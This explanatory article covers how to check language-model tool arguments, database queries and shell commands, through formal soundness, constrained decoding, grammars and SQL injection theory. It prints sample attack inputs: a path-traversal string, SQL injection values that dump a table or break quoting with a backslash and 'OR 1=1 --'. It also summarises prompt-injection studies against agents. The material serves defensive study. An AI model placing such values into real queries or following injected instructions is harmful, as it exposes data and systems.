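# Checking the arguments that language models write for tools, database queries and shell commands

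## What is checked, and what a check can promise

A large language model is a program that generates text. Developers connect these models to software that acts on what they write. For example, a database runs a query, a shell runs a command, or a payment function takes an amount. An agent is a model that works through a task by calling other programs. An *argument* is any text or value that a model writes and another program will act on, and the *sink* is the component that acts on it. Checking an argument means deciding whether the sink can safely receive it. The methods come mostly from older work on programming languages and computer security, and the assurance they provide ranges from a measured error rate to a mathematical proof.

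### From text to action

According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers who build on its Claude models, the model "never runs anything on its own". The developer supplies a list of tools, each with a name and a schema, which lists the fields the tool takes and their types. The model responds with a request that names a tool and fills in the fields. The developer's application then runs the operation and sends the result back, and the model continues. A few tools, such as web search, run on Anthropic's own servers. Their operations have usually finished before the application receives anything, so a check inside the application would come too late.

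Here is the core of a request from Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, without its identifiers:

```json
{
  "name": "get_weather",
  "input": { "location": "San Francisco, CA", "unit": "celsius" }
}
```

The arguments are written in JSON, a common notation for nested fields and values. OpenAI's *Function calling* describes a procedure in which they arrive as one string, which the application must parse before it can call the function.

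A database query is also text, in a language of its own:

```sql
SELECT title, price FROM books WHERE author = 'Le Guin';
```

So is a command line. This one is the start of a script in a paper by Li, Lazarek and colleagues, in *RT*, a system that checks shell programs before they run:

```sh
find . | grep -E 'book[0-9]+\.txt' | xargs cat
```

The command lists the files below the current folder, keeps those whose names contain "book", a number and ".txt", and prints their contents. It is well formed but has a bug its writer did not intend. `xargs` splits its input at spaces, so a file named `my book1.txt` reaches `cat` as two separate file names.

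One of these forms can contain another. For example, Anthropic publishes a schema for a tool that runs shell commands, and a call to such a tool is a JSON object that contains a whole command line. The JSON can be valid even if the command would erase a disk.

### Where unsafe arguments come from

The plainest cause is error. A model supplies an option that the installed program does not have, or the wrong customer's number.

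Another is prompt injection, in which the model reads text, such as a web page or an email, and follows it as an instruction. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* that language models do not inherently separate instructions from data, and that defences which train or prompt a model to do so impose the distinction on a technology that lacks it. Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks* quotes the centre's conclusion that such attacks "may never be totally mitigated". Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, trace the attacker's text through the model and into ordinary sinks such as databases, command runners and web requests. In their analysis, the model usually carries the attacker's influence to a component that trusts its output, rather than creating the vulnerability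 itself. They built a small web application and tested seven models with five attack scenarios meant to make the server send requests it should not. Susceptibility varied substantially between models, so changing the model can change the odds that an attack succeeds, but it does not fix the vulnerable component.

A model may also pursue something that nobody asked for. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) reports that a model trained for long-running tasks failed in ways the company's existing tests had not captured. The model's persistence gave it more opportunities to take unwanted actions. OpenAI paused internal access and restored it in limited form after adding evaluations and monitoring.

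A query that deletes a table has the same effect whether the model made a mistake, followed a stranger's instruction or pursued some aim of its own. A check can therefore enforce a rule against the deletion by looking only at the query, without establishing why the model wrote it. This is the main advantage of checking arguments, but the query alone is not always enough. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe an outsider whose plain-language request for a table of users becomes an ordinary read query, one that an administrator might also have wanted. To distinguish the outsider's query from the administrator's, a check needs the argument's provenance, the record of which sources contributed to it.

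### The safe set, and two ways to get it wrong

A *policy* is a written rule that specifies which arguments a sink may receive, and the *safe set* is the set of those arguments. The policy can depend on the state of the system. For example, a refund for order 1182 may be in the safe set while the order belongs to the logged-in customer, but not after the order has been refunded.

If *S* is the safe set and *A* is the set of arguments that a check accepts, the check is *sound* when *A* ⊆ *S*, so that it never passes an unsafe argument, and *exact* when *A* = *S*. *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) gives the same definitions in terms of a policy, which is a set of forbidden strings, and a guard, which is a computable function that blocks or passes each output. A guard is sound if it blocks every forbidden output, "permissive" if it passes every permitted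 output, and exact if it does both. A guard can trivially be sound by blocking everything or permissive by passing everything, but for some policies no program can be both.

Take a tool that reads a file and returns its contents, with the policy that the file must lie inside the folder `/srv/reports`.

A check that accepts any path beginning with `/srv/reports/` is unsound. The path `/srv/reports/../keys.txt` passes, but `..` means "the folder above", so the tool would read `/srv/keys.txt`.

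A stricter check accepts only `/srv/reports/`, then lower-case letters, then `.txt`. It rejects any path with dots or slashes in the middle, but it also rejects `/srv/reports/q3.txt`, a legitimate file with a digit in its name. A *precise* check rarely rejects a safe argument, so this one is sound but not very precise. A check that first works out which file the path refers to and then compares folders is close to exact.

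Precision is a matter of degree, and people measure it in different ways. Bertrand Meyer, a software engineering professor writing in Communications of the ACM, defines it as the share of rejections that are real violations, so a check that rejects 40 cases, 30 of them rightly, has a precision of 0.75. Papers on guards often give the false-positive rate instead, which is the share of harmless inputs that the guard rejects. Meyer thinks missed violations are generally worse than false alarms, but he notes that people abandon a tool that raises too many false alarms. He also notes that soundness and precision both depend on what has been declared a violation. For example, a fraud detector that declines a genuine purchase is imprecise from the bank's point of view but unsound from that of the customer, who wants a card that works whenever there is credit.

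Real checks sometimes block valid calls and sometimes let forbidden ones through, and the same mistake can cause either error. *NOMOS* (2026) describes a compiler that turns written policies into checks on tool calls, and one of its tests looks for rules that refer to a field the tool does not have. In *NOMOS* itself, such a rule would block the tool permanently; the test caught eight cases in an airline policy and one in a retail policy. In the version for AgentDojo, a security benchmark for agents, the same defect made a prohibition evaluate to "false", so the rule never fired and the call went through.

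Other checks accept some unsoundness by design. *Look Before You Leap* (2026) presents a verifier for shell commands that compares a command's options with those in the program's help text. It could extract at least one option for 91.1% of tools. For the rest, it has no list to compare with, so it accepts the command. Its syntax check is exact because it calls the shell's own parser. A verifier can be exact about one property and unsound about another, so a claim of soundness means little unless it names the property.

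*CARE* (2026) presents another guard for shell commands and reports a false-positive rate of 0.91% and an F1 score of 85.64%. The F1 score combines the share of harmful commands caught with the share of alarms that were correct. These figures are useful for choosing a guard, but they describe average behaviour on one collection of commands, and an attacker is not limited to that collection.

These definitions all apply to one argument at a time, but a task can go wrong even when each step is acceptable on its own. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), cites an experiment in which a guard blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. This is a single study, and the survey calls for independent replication.

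### Describing a set of strings

A safe set is often infinite, so a policy needs a finite description of it. Computer scientists call any set of strings a language, and policies mostly use two kinds.

A *regular expression* is a pattern. `[0-9]` stands for any digit and `+` for "one or more", so `[0-9]+` describes all non-empty strings of digits. A *finite automaton* is a machine that recognises such a set by reading one character at a time and remembering only which of a fixed number of states it is in. The automaton for `[0-9]+` needs three states:

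| State | On a digit, go to | On anything else, go to | Accept if the input ends here? |
|---|---|---|---|
| start | digits | dead | no |
| digits | digits | dead | yes |
| dead | dead | dead | no |

The string `42` ends in "digits", and the automaton accepts it. `4x` ends in "dead", and the empty string never leaves "start". Regular expressions and finite automata describe exactly the same sets, the *regular languages*. (Many programming tools add features to their patterns that go beyond this. Li and colleagues leave those features out, because with them no algorithm could always decide whether one language lies inside another.)

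A finite automaton cannot match brackets to arbitrary depth, since it would have to remember how many are still open. A *context-free grammar* can. It is a list of rewriting rules, such as:

```
expr → number
expr → ( expr )
```

These rules generate `7`, `(7)` and `((7))` from `expr`, but never `((7)`. JSON objects and database queries can both be nested, so a full description of either needs this kind of grammar. Every regular language is also context-free.

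OpenAI lets developers attach either kind of description to a tool that takes free text. Its example regular expression matches timestamps made up of a month's name, a one- or two-digit day, a four-digit year, and an hour with AM or PM. Both "August 7th 2025 at 10AM" and "February 99th 2025 at 10AM" match. A tighter pattern could exclude February 99th, but no fixed pattern can check whether order 1182 belongs to the current customer, because that information is in the database.

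### Three places to act

A developer can intervene while the model is writing. *Constrained decoding* restricts the model's choice of each next token, the fragment of text it generates at one step, so that the output always belongs to a given set of strings. In OpenAI's strict mode, a tool's schema defines that set. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) describes a system called Agent-C that goes further by sampling tool calls until one complies with a policy. If it runs out of attempts, it returns a call that reports an error. For the file tool, the developer could allow only strings of the form `/srv/reports/[a-z]+\.txt`. The model could then never write the path to the keys, though it could still pick the wrong report.

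Alternatively, the application can let the model write freely and test the concrete argument immediately before the sink receives it, which is a *check at use*. This check can consult the current state of the system, so it can handle the refund that was proper a minute ago but no longer is. It also works the same way for any model. Its weakness is that a refusal comes in the middle of a task, and the application then needs a way to handle it. Amer and colleagues distinguish a guard, which examines a program before it runs, from a monitor, which examines each action just before the program performs it and can stop the program there. They favour controlling actions at the point where they happen over judging the text that requests them in advance.

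The remaining option is to prove, before deployment, that every argument that could reach the sink is safe. If *P* is the set of possible arguments, the claim is *P* ⊆ *S*, a *language inclusion*. Since *P* is rarely known exactly, the proof uses a larger set *P′* that certainly contains it, and shows that *P* ⊆ *P′* ⊆ *S*. Li and colleagues do this for shell pipelines, using regular expressions as types to check that each command can accept everything the previous one may output. When the inclusion fails, their tool prints a *witness*, a concrete string that violates it. For the pipeline above, the witness is `./ book0.txt`, where the space causes the problem.

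A sound check on arguments can err only by being too strict. Li and colleagues apply "sound" instead to a description of what may occur, which can be too large and still be sound. If the lines in a stream can only be `foo` and `bar`, they call the type `foo` unsound because it omits `bar`, and the type `.*`, which matches anything, sound but imprecise.

A proof of this kind needs something to restrict *P* first. A model that writes freely can produce any string, so *P* ⊆ *S* holds only if every string is safe. Suppose instead that the model supplies only a name, the application accepts only lower-case letters, and fixed code adds `/srv/reports/` before the name and `.txt` after it. Every path this code can build is then in *S*, no matter why the model produced the name or who influenced it.

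### What a guarantee rests on

Every such guarantee depends on a *trusted base*, the set of components that must work correctly for it to hold. The term comes from computer security, where the *trusted computing base (TCB)* entry in the glossary of NIST, the US standards institute, covers all the hardware, firmware and software that together enforce a security policy. For a check at use, the trusted base includes the code of the check and the code that blocks every other route to the sink. It need not include the model, whose behaviour is harder to guarantee than that of any other part of the system. *CARE* loses some of this advantage when it sends borderline commands to a language model for judgement.

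The check must also interpret the argument as the sink will. *Look Before You Leap* ensures this in its structural test by using the shell's own parser, since an imitation could parse some unusual inputs differently. Even the proof about `/srv/reports` assumes that a path in the folder leads to a file in the folder. If someone places a symbolic link there, which redirects to a file elsewhere, the string still has the approved form but the tool reads the keys. Li and colleagues' results similarly depend on a hand-written database of what each shell command accepts and produces, and a wrong entry can make a faulty pipeline pass.

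Settings are also part of the trusted base. If a developer does not set OpenAI's strict option, one of the company's two interfaces tries to convert the schema to strict form and falls back to best-effort generation if it cannot. The response then shows `strict: false`, so an application that relies on the schema has to check that field.

The policy is also part of the base, because even a flawless check will enforce a wrong rule. On one benchmark in the survey by Dantas and colleagues, language models translated ordinary English into a formal planning language with the correct meaning only 24.8% to 34.2% of the time.

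## Constraining what the model can generate

Suppose a shop gives a model a refund tool. The tool takes an order number of exactly eight digits and an amount in whole dollars, up to 500. As regular expressions, with `{8}` for "eight times", `?` after an optional item and `|` between alternatives, the two fields are:

```
order    [0-9]{8}
amount   [1-9][0-9]?|[1-4][0-9][0-9]|500
```

The second pattern matches 1 to 99, 100 to 499, or 500. Constrained decoding can enforce both patterns during generation, so the model never writes a seven-digit order number or a refund of 900 dollars.

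### The token mask

At each step a language model gives every token in its vocabulary a probability of coming next, and the decoder, the code that runs the model, picks one. A constrained decoder first removes the tokens that cannot lead to a permitted string. If the text so far is *w*, a token *t* stays available only if some continuation *v* makes the whole string *wtv* permitted. *ChopChop* (Nagy, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) calls a prefix "completable" when such a continuation exists. The list of available and blocked tokens is called the *token mask*.

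For the order number, the automaton only has to count. It has one state for each number of digits from zero to eight and a dead state for everything else, and it accepts in state eight. To test a token, the decoder runs the token's characters through the automaton from the current state and blocks the token if it ends up in the dead state. Tokens often hold several digits, so suppose the vocabulary contains every string of one, two or three digits:

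| Digits so far | Candidate token | Result |
|---|---|---|
| none | `104` | available, five digits to go |
| `104` | `882` | available, two digits to go |
| `104882` | `731` | blocked, would make nine digits |
| `104882` | closing quotation mark | blocked, only six digits |
| `104882` | `73` | available, completes the number |
| `10488273` | `1` | blocked |
| `10488273` | closing quotation mark | available |

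Some tokens run past the end of a field, such as one made up of a digit, a quotation mark and a comma, and the decoder has to test the whole token. *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding* (Li, Rahili and Zhao, 2025) reports that an earlier system could accept a long token because its beginning was valid, even though its ending was not. The paper's own decoder keeps the part of the token that fits the current pattern and requires the next pattern to start from there.

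They also explain how a number of variable length ends. A pattern such as `[0-9]+` can match digits forever, and a model trained on complete programs almost never produces its stop token halfway through one. They therefore extend the pattern to include the symbols that may follow the number, and the model ends the number by writing one of them. In the refund call, a comma or closing brace ends the amount. After `50`, the mask allows both another `0` and the closing brace, so the model's probabilities determine whether the refund is 50 or 500.

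After blocking the illegal tokens, the decoder rescales the remaining probabilities to add up to one, then samples. If it computes the mask correctly, every finished string belongs to the language, whatever the model or prompt, even if the prompt contains an attacker's instructions. This does not hold for unfinished strings. Zhang, Xu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Constrained LLM Generation over a Refinement Order of Grammar Fragments* that a model can use up its token budget in the middle of a legal prefix. An application that receives `{"order": "1048` should treat the call as failed and not try to repair it.

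### What a schema can express

A provider's JSON Schema mode applies the same rule to a whole tool call. The engine translates the schema into a grammar, and the mask then enforces the brackets and quotation marks, the field names, the type of each value and any fixed list of permitted values. For the refund tool, the part of the schema that describes the fields could be:

```json
{
  "order":  { "type": "string", "pattern": "^[0-9]{8}$" },
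  "amount": { "type": "integer", "minimum": 1, "maximum": 500 }
}
```

The shop's limits are in `pattern`, `minimum` and `maximum`. An engine that enforced only the types would allow the order number `banana` and a refund of 90,000 dollars. Developers therefore need to look up each keyword in the provider's documentation. An engine that does not support a keyword may reject the schema, which is harmless, or ignore the keyword, which leaves the limit as only a hint to the model. If `maximum` is not supported, developers can use OpenAI's free-text tools, which accept a regular expression, because the pattern for the amount already contains the cap. The application can also check that the amount does not exceed 500 when the call arrives.

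JSON Schema cannot express some constraints, such as the requirement that a name used in one field be declared in an earlier one. Zhang and colleagues enforce this requirement with a grammar that changes during generation.

An application can build the list of allowed values from live data. Glenn, Samuel and Liu (2025), in *Play by the Type Rules*, do this in a query language that lets an SQL query put questions to a model. The constraint depends on how the query uses the answer. If the query tests whether the answer is greater than 40, the decoder allows only an integer. If the query compares the answer with a `city` column, the decoder allows only values that occur in that column. Without this constraint, a model might correctly answer "Washington D.C." but the query would find no match, because the table has "Washington DC". The largest gain in accuracy was 6.6 percentage points, on 1,000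 questions that combine tables and text. It came when a model with 3 billion parameters (the numbers adjusted during training, a rough measure of size) answered the questions in queries that a 70-billion-parameter model had written.

The shop could use the same method. Before the model writes the call, the application looks up the logged-in customer's orders and passes those order numbers as the only permitted values, so the model cannot name anyone else's order. However, if somebody refunds an order after the lookup, its number is still on the list.

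### Constraints on whole programs

When the argument is a program, a grammar can ensure only that it parses, which leaves most errors in place. Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, cite a finding that about 94% of the compilation errors in model-written TypeScript are type errors and about 6% are purely syntactic. TypeScript is a form of JavaScript whose compiler checks types, for instance that a function expecting a number does not receive text.

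Types are harder to enforce than syntax because the decoder has to check unfinished code. Nagy and colleagues give the example of `1 + myString`. As a complete expression it would probably be a type error, but the model may be about to write `1 + myString.length`, which is valid and which a decoder that blocks `myString` would prevent.

Mündler and colleagues built a type-constrained decoder for TypeScript in 2025. As Biagiola and colleagues describe it, the decoder draws candidate tokens according to the model's probabilities, appends one to the program and runs a parser and a type checker that both handle incomplete code. It keeps the token if the result can still become a well-typed program, and otherwise tries the next candidate. The implementation covers most of TypeScript but leaves out imports, user-defined types, type inference and forward references, which are uses of a function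 before its definition.

ChopChop, a general framework built by Nagy and colleagues, lets users program their own constraints on a model's output. Users write these constraints over syntax trees, the nested structures that a parser makes out of text. ChopChop turns the unfinished text into the set of all trees that its completions could produce, removes the trees that break the constraint and tests whether any are left. This last test is called the *realizability check*.

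Suppose the model must write a sum of odd numbers with an even total, and it has written `1+2` so far. The decoder blocks the token `+` because it would complete the number 2, which is even, and leave no valid tree. It allows the token `2` because `1+22` can still become `1+221`. The set of possible trees is infinite, but ChopChop can store it as a finite structure with loops, much as an automaton with three states can describe infinitely many strings of digits.

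In general, no algorithm can decide whether such a set contains a valid program, even when checking one finished program is easy. Users therefore often write constraints that only approximate the right set. If the approximation keeps a dead end, the decoder wastes time but does not return an invalid program, because it tests the finished program first. If the approximation removes a valid program, the model can no longer write it.

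This second kind of error matters for the framework's theorem about probabilities. A realizability check is *complete* if it never rejects a set that contains a valid program. With a complete check, every valid program that the unconstrained model could produce is at least as likely under the constraint. The theorem covers top-k and top-p sampling, two common methods that draw each token from a short list of the most likely ones. It does not cover every method. In a deterministic search that keeps several partial programs at once, discarding a dead end can make room for a different prefix, which may change the final answer.

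Nagy and colleagues tested three open models, with 6.7 to 13 billion parameters, on 72 TypeScript tasks at five temperatures (a setting for how random the sampling is). Adding up their results over 1,080 runs per method gives:

| Method | Programs that compiled |
|---|---|
| no constraint | 781 |
| grammar only | 651 |
| ChopChop with a type constraint | 932 |
| the tool by Mündler and colleagues | 1,035 |

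A program counted as a success if it compiled, whether or not it solved the task. The grammar did worse than generating without constraints, probably because it covered only a small part of TypeScript and blocked valid code outside that part. The tool by Mündler and colleagues covers more of the language.

In a second test, models had to rewrite short programs in a toy language without changing what the programs compute. This time the prompts asked for the code between markers, so that stray commentary would not count against a model. The unconstrained models succeeded in 26 of 150 runs, and ChopChop raised this to 124. In one failed run constrained by the grammar alone, a model wrote an English sentence that began "Here is an equivalent refactored version", and the sentence parsed because a row of words in that grammar is a series of function calls.

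### Allowing only names that exist

That sentence was syntactically valid but referred to functions and variables that did not exist. Zhang and colleagues call such a name a "ghost reference". It may be an undeclared variable, a column missing from the table or an option that a command does not have. An ordinary grammar cannot exclude it, because all the grammar says about the position is that some identifier goes there. Their *decode-time grammars* replace the identifier with a list of the names that exist when the model reaches that point. For a command that switches between branches (parallel versions of a code base), the grammar might be:

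```
checkout → "git checkout " branch
branch   → "main" | "dev" | "release-2.0" | "hotfix-login"
```

If the model then writes a command that creates a branch, the system adds the new name to the list before the next command.

They prove that the output cannot contain a ghost reference if every position for a name uses such a list, and every list is non-empty and contains only declared names. The proof also assumes that the developer has marked every position where a name can occur and that the masking engine follows the grammar exactly. They tested the engine with 90 permitted strings and 772 forbidden ones, and it classified all of them correctly. Some of the names contained quotation marks and vertical bars, which have a meaning in the grammar's notation. Because the names come from data, someone could choose a branch name that rewrites the constraint if these characters weren't properly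 escaped.

If a list is empty, the system can fall back to allowing any identifier, which removes the guarantee at that position.

Zhang and colleagues also show that no finite set of grammars prepared in advance could replace the changing list. Programs can declare infinitely many sets of names, so at least two of those sets would share a grammar. That grammar would then either allow a name that one of the programs has not declared or block a name that it has.

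On 60 database questions, the small model Qwen3-0.6B returned the correct rows 70% of the time without constraints and named 11 columns that did not exist. Listing the legal columns in the prompt raised accuracy to 93.3% and reduced the nonexistent columns to four. Retrying failed queries gave 90% accuracy and five nonexistent columns. With the mask, accuracy was 100% and the model named no nonexistent columns. The paper also compares the mask with a version that fixes the rest of the query but leaves the column name open. That version scored 0%, far below the unconstrained model, so comparing the mask with it exaggerates the mask's benefit.

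A model limited to names that exist can still choose the wrong kind of thing. In a program for graphics processors, an operation needs a buffer, a named block of memory, of a particular shape. When the list of allowed names contained all four buffers of the right general kind, Qwen3-0.6B chose one of the wrong shape in 4 of 160 choices (2.5%). When the system also filtered the list by shape, only two buffers remained, both of the right shape, so the error rate would be 0% for any model. The 2.5% comes from 20 programs generated by one very small model, so it is weak evidence of how often a larger model would make this mistake. Even with the shape filter, the model can still confuse two buffers of the same shape. On the same kind of program, all eight samples generated under the constraint compiled, but only 62% computed the right numbers.

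The extra work slowed generation by 10.6% to 17.8% compared with XGrammar, a widely used masking engine.

### What the constraint costs

The mask can slow generation, but the bigger problem is that it changes which valid answer the model is likely to give. This can happen even with a tool as simple as the refund tool.

Suppose the order field accepts either eight digits or the word `none`, and the customer has quoted a nine-digit invoice number by mistake. The model starts copying the invoice number with probability 0.9 and writes `none` with probability 0.1. After copying eight digits, it adds the ninth with probability 0.99 and stops with probability 0.01. Without a mask, the output is valid with probability 0.9 × 0.01 + 0.1 = 0.109, and about 92% of the valid outputs are `none`. With the mask, the model can still copy the first eight digits, since they could form an order number. The mask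 then blocks the ninth digit and the model has to stop, so it writes a truncated invoice number 90% of the time.

ChopChop's theorem holds here because neither valid output has become less likely. The probability of `none` is still 0.1, and that of the truncated number has risen from 0.009 to 0.9. The theorem does not guarantee that the ratio between these probabilities stays the same. For the shop, the result is worse than an error message, because any check would have caught a nine-digit order number, but the truncated one looks valid and might be another customer's order. Generating without constraints and retrying until the output is valid would preserve the ratio, but it would take about nine attempts on average.

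Biagiola and colleagues measured the effect on whole programs by counting the solutions that passed all the tests. They ran the TypeScript decoder by Mündler and colleagues with six open models on 159 programming problems, and with two of those models on another 390, ten times at each of three temperatures. The models did significantly better without the constraint in all but two configurations, where the difference was not significant. At the lowest temperature, Qwen-2.5-32B solved 82.3% of the first set without the constraint and 72.3% with it. The much smaller Gemma-2-2B solved 35.7% without it and 32.0% with it.

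They trace most of the loss to valid programs that the decoder does not support. Of 4,231 programs that Gemma-2-2B wrote without the constraint and that compiled, the decoder's type checker rejected 982. In one of them, the model calls a function `isPalindrome` and defines it further down, which TypeScript allows. The decoder blocks the call because the function is not yet defined. Under the constraint, the model had already written `is`, so it continued with `isNaN`, a built-in function that tests for something else. The program compiled but gave wrong answers. In other cases, the model repeated itself until it ran out of time. ChopChop's theorem does not apply here because it requires a check that never blocks a valid program.

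Several replies to this result mostly agree about the cause. One solution is to train the model to stay within the supported part of the language. Biagiola and colleagues rewarded two models for programs that the decoder's checker accepts. On the first problem set, Qwen-2.5-32B gained 5.3 percentage points under the constraint but still scored about 5 points below unconstrained generation. Gemma-2-2B closed the gap, but partly because its unconstrained score fell. A better solution is a constraint that covers the whole language. They built one for TOML, a simple format for configuration files, and constrained decoding then beat unconstrained generation by 2.5% for a 32-billion-parameter model and by up to 54% for a 2-billion-parameter one. When they removed features from the constraint, correctness fell by as much as 97%.

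Another response is to constrain less of the text. In *Thinking Before Constraining*, Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026) let the model reason in ordinary prose and apply the mask only to the final answer. On grade-school maths problems, LLaMA3-8B scored 66.2% with free text, 48.9% when its reasoning also had to fit inside a JSON field, and 77.9% when only the final answer was constrained. Part of the gain over free text is an artefact, because the scoring script searched for the answer after a set phrase and missed some correct answers. When a larger model extracted the answers from the same free text, the score was 74.7%. The harm from constraining the reasoning evidently depends on the model, since Gemma2-9B scored 84.2% with the constraint and 82.7% with free text. Tool calls can easily use the late switch, because only the call reaches the sink and the reasoning can stay unconstrained.

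There is also evidence that constrained decoding makes function calls more accurate. Dang and Ermon (2026, *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata*) tested it on diffusion language models, which fill in many positions of a text at once. A token-by-token mask does not work for these models because, if both `1.` and `.1` are valid numbers, choosing each position separately can produce `..`. Their method uses the automaton to compute probabilities for whole valid strings at each step. On a benchmark of function calls, it raised the accuracy of Dream-7B from 63.9% to 71.5% when the model always took its most likely output, and from 22.3% to 69.0% with random sampling. Most language models write from left to right, so the size of the gain may not carry over to them.

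The refund schema is more like TOML and function calls than TypeScript. It includes every call the shop would want to accept, so the losses from unsupported features should not occur. The invoice number is still a problem, and adding `none` to the schema helps only if the model chooses `none` before writing the first digit.

### A valid refund for the wrong order

Consider this call:

```json
{ "order": "10488273", "amount": 480 }
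```

The refund call satisfies the schema, but the order may belong to someone else, the item may have cost only 60 dollars, or the shop may already have paid the refund. Restricting the order number to a list of the customer's own orders prevents the call from naming someone else's order. A decode-time grammar could prevent an excessive refund by looking up the price once the model has written the order number and capping the amount at that price. Whether the shop has already paid the refund still has to be checked when the call is executed.

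Even then, the model may refund headphones from one of the customer's orders when the customer asked to return a charger from another. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge the same limit for names, since they guarantee only that a name exists. The mask also doesn't check who chose the value, so it allows an order number planted in an email as readily as one the customer typed.

The guarantee also depends on the correctness of the engine that computes the mask and of the translation from schema to grammar, both of which often run on the provider's machines. The mask also doesn't constrain calls that reach the tool by another route, such as those from a backup model that runs without strict mode. The application can cover both cases by testing the two patterns again when the call arrives, which takes one line of code per field. That second test then keeps malformed values away from the sink, and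 the mask mainly ensures that the test rarely fails. Because the test guarantees that the order number is always eight digits, a developer can rely on this when proving properties of the database query that receives it.

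## A value placed inside a fixed database query

When the refund call arrives, the shop's application has to find the order in its database. The simplest code pastes the order number between two quotation marks in a query that the developer wrote in advance, and eight digits can do no harm there. Names are less predictable. Suppose a model answers customers of a bookshop, and the application builds its query like this:

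```python
query = "SELECT title, price FROM books WHERE author = '" + name + "';"
```

The developer fixes everything except `name`, which the model supplies. `Le Guin` works as intended. If the model supplies `A' OR 'a' LIKE 'a`, the application sends this:

```sql
SELECT title, price FROM books WHERE author = 'A' OR 'a' LIKE 'a';
```

The text `'a'` matches the pattern `'a'` in every row, so the database returns the whole table. That is harmless for a list of books, but the same trick in a query that checks passwords lets an attacker log in without a password.

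### What counts as an injection

Su and Wassermann (2006), in *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications*, define the attack by its effect on the query's parse tree, the syntax tree that the database builds before running the query. Here are the trees for the two conditions above, slightly simplified:

```
Le Guin                         A' OR 'a' LIKE 'a

comparison                      OR
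├─ author                       ├─ comparison
├─ =                            │  ├─ author = 'A'
└─ string                       └─ comparison
   └─ Le Guin                      └─ 'a' LIKE 'a'
```

In the tree for `Le Guin`, one node covers exactly the text that the model supplied. The longer value starts inside one string, continues through an operator and ends inside another string, so no single node covers exactly that text.

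In the formal definition, the developer chooses which kinds of node a supplied value may fill, such as the contents of a string or a number. A query is an injection attack if it parses and at least one supplied value is not the complete text under a node of a chosen kind. A query that does not parse is not an attack, because the database refuses to run it. The definition also assumes that the fixed text expresses what the developer wanted, so fixed text that deletes a table by mistake counts as a bug rather than an injection.

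Su and Wassermann implemented the definition as a runtime check called SQLCHECK. It surrounds each supplied value with special marker characters. After the application assembles the query, SQLCHECK parses it with a grammar that allows the markers only around a complete parse-tree node of a chosen kind. If the query parses, SQLCHECK removes the markers and sends the query to the database. It took about 3 milliseconds per query and made no errors on a collection of real attacks and legitimate inputs, most of which an independent group had compiled.

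Ray and Ligatti (2012), in *Defining Code-injection Attacks*, object to the definition based on the parse tree. If a query compares a PIN with an unquoted value, an attacker can supply `exit()`. This is a complete function call and fills one node, so the definition misses it unless the developer has excluded function calls. The definition also reports attacks when nobody has injected any code. For example, an application may join a file name and an extension inside one pair of quotation marks, so that neither value fills the whole string. Ray and Ligatti propose counting supplied text as code unless it lies inside a finished piece of data, such as a string or a number, with no variables in it.

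For one value between quotation marks, the disagreement hardly matters. If the value stays inside its string, it is harmless under both definitions.

### A safe set for the quoted value

After the opening quotation mark, the database reads every character as ordinary content until something ends the string or changes how it reads the next character. A quotation mark can end the string. In some databases, including MySQL with its usual settings, a backslash can change how the database reads the next character, so `\'` stands for a quotation mark that is part of the content.

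The backslash is dangerous even when no supplied value contains a quotation mark. Suppose the query has two conditions, and the model supplies `\` as the author and ` OR 1=1 -- ` as the title:

```sql
SELECT title, price FROM books WHERE author = '\' AND title = ' OR 1=1 -- ';
```

The backslash escapes the quotation mark that should close the author value, so the string continues until the mark that should open the title. The database then reads `OR 1=1` as code and treats everything after `--` as a comment.

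The safe set *S* contains every string that has no single quotation mark (the apostrophe character) and no backslash. When the database reads a value in *S*, the first single quotation mark it reaches is the one the developer wrote after the value. The query therefore has the same structure for every value in *S*, with only the content of one string changing, so no value in *S* can cause an injection.

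*S* is smaller than it has to be. In standard SQL, two apostrophes in a row inside a string represent one, so `O''Brian` would be harmless, but it is not in *S*. A conservative safe set like this one makes the check less precise, but the check is still sound and the set is very easy to describe.

### Testing the inclusion

Suppose the application accepts only values that match some pattern, and let *T* be the set of strings that match it. The developer wants to show that *T* ⊆ *S*. *T* may be infinite, so the developer can't check every string in it. The usual algorithm looks for a counterexample, a string in *T* but not in *S*. If none exists, the inclusion holds.

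The search needs an automaton for the unsafe strings. One for *S* has two states. It starts in "clean", moves to "broken" at the first quotation mark or backslash, and stays there. It accepts a string that ends in "clean". Swapping the accepting and non-accepting states gives the *complement*, which accepts exactly the strings that are not in *S*, so it accepts in "broken". (The swap works because the automaton always has exactly one next state. If it could follow several paths at once, the same string might end in both kinds of state.)

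Now take a query that stores a hostname:

```sql
INSERT INTO hosts VALUES ('example.com');
```

In this example, the value must match the pattern `[a-z0-9.-]+`, which allows one or more lower-case letters, digits, dots and hyphens. The pattern's automaton has three states, "start", "host" and "dead", and accepts in "host". The pattern is looser than the real rules for hostnames, since it also matches the string `...`, but a proof that covers every string the pattern matches also covers the real hostnames.

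The *product* of the two automata runs both on the same input and records a pair of states. It starts in (start, clean), and these are all the pairs it can reach:

| Current pair | Letter a–z, digit, dot or hyphen | Quotation mark or backslash | Anything else |
|---|---|---|---|
| start, clean | host, clean | dead, broken | dead, clean |
| host, clean | host, clean | dead, broken | dead, clean |
| dead, clean | dead, clean | dead, broken | dead, clean |
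| dead, broken | dead, broken | dead, broken | dead, broken |

A counterexample would have to end in (host, broken), because the pattern accepts in "host" and the complement accepts in "broken". No row leads to that state, so the product accepts nothing, and every string that matches the pattern is in *S*. This covers infinitely many hostnames, including `a--b`, whose two hyphens would start a comment if they were outside the quotation marks.

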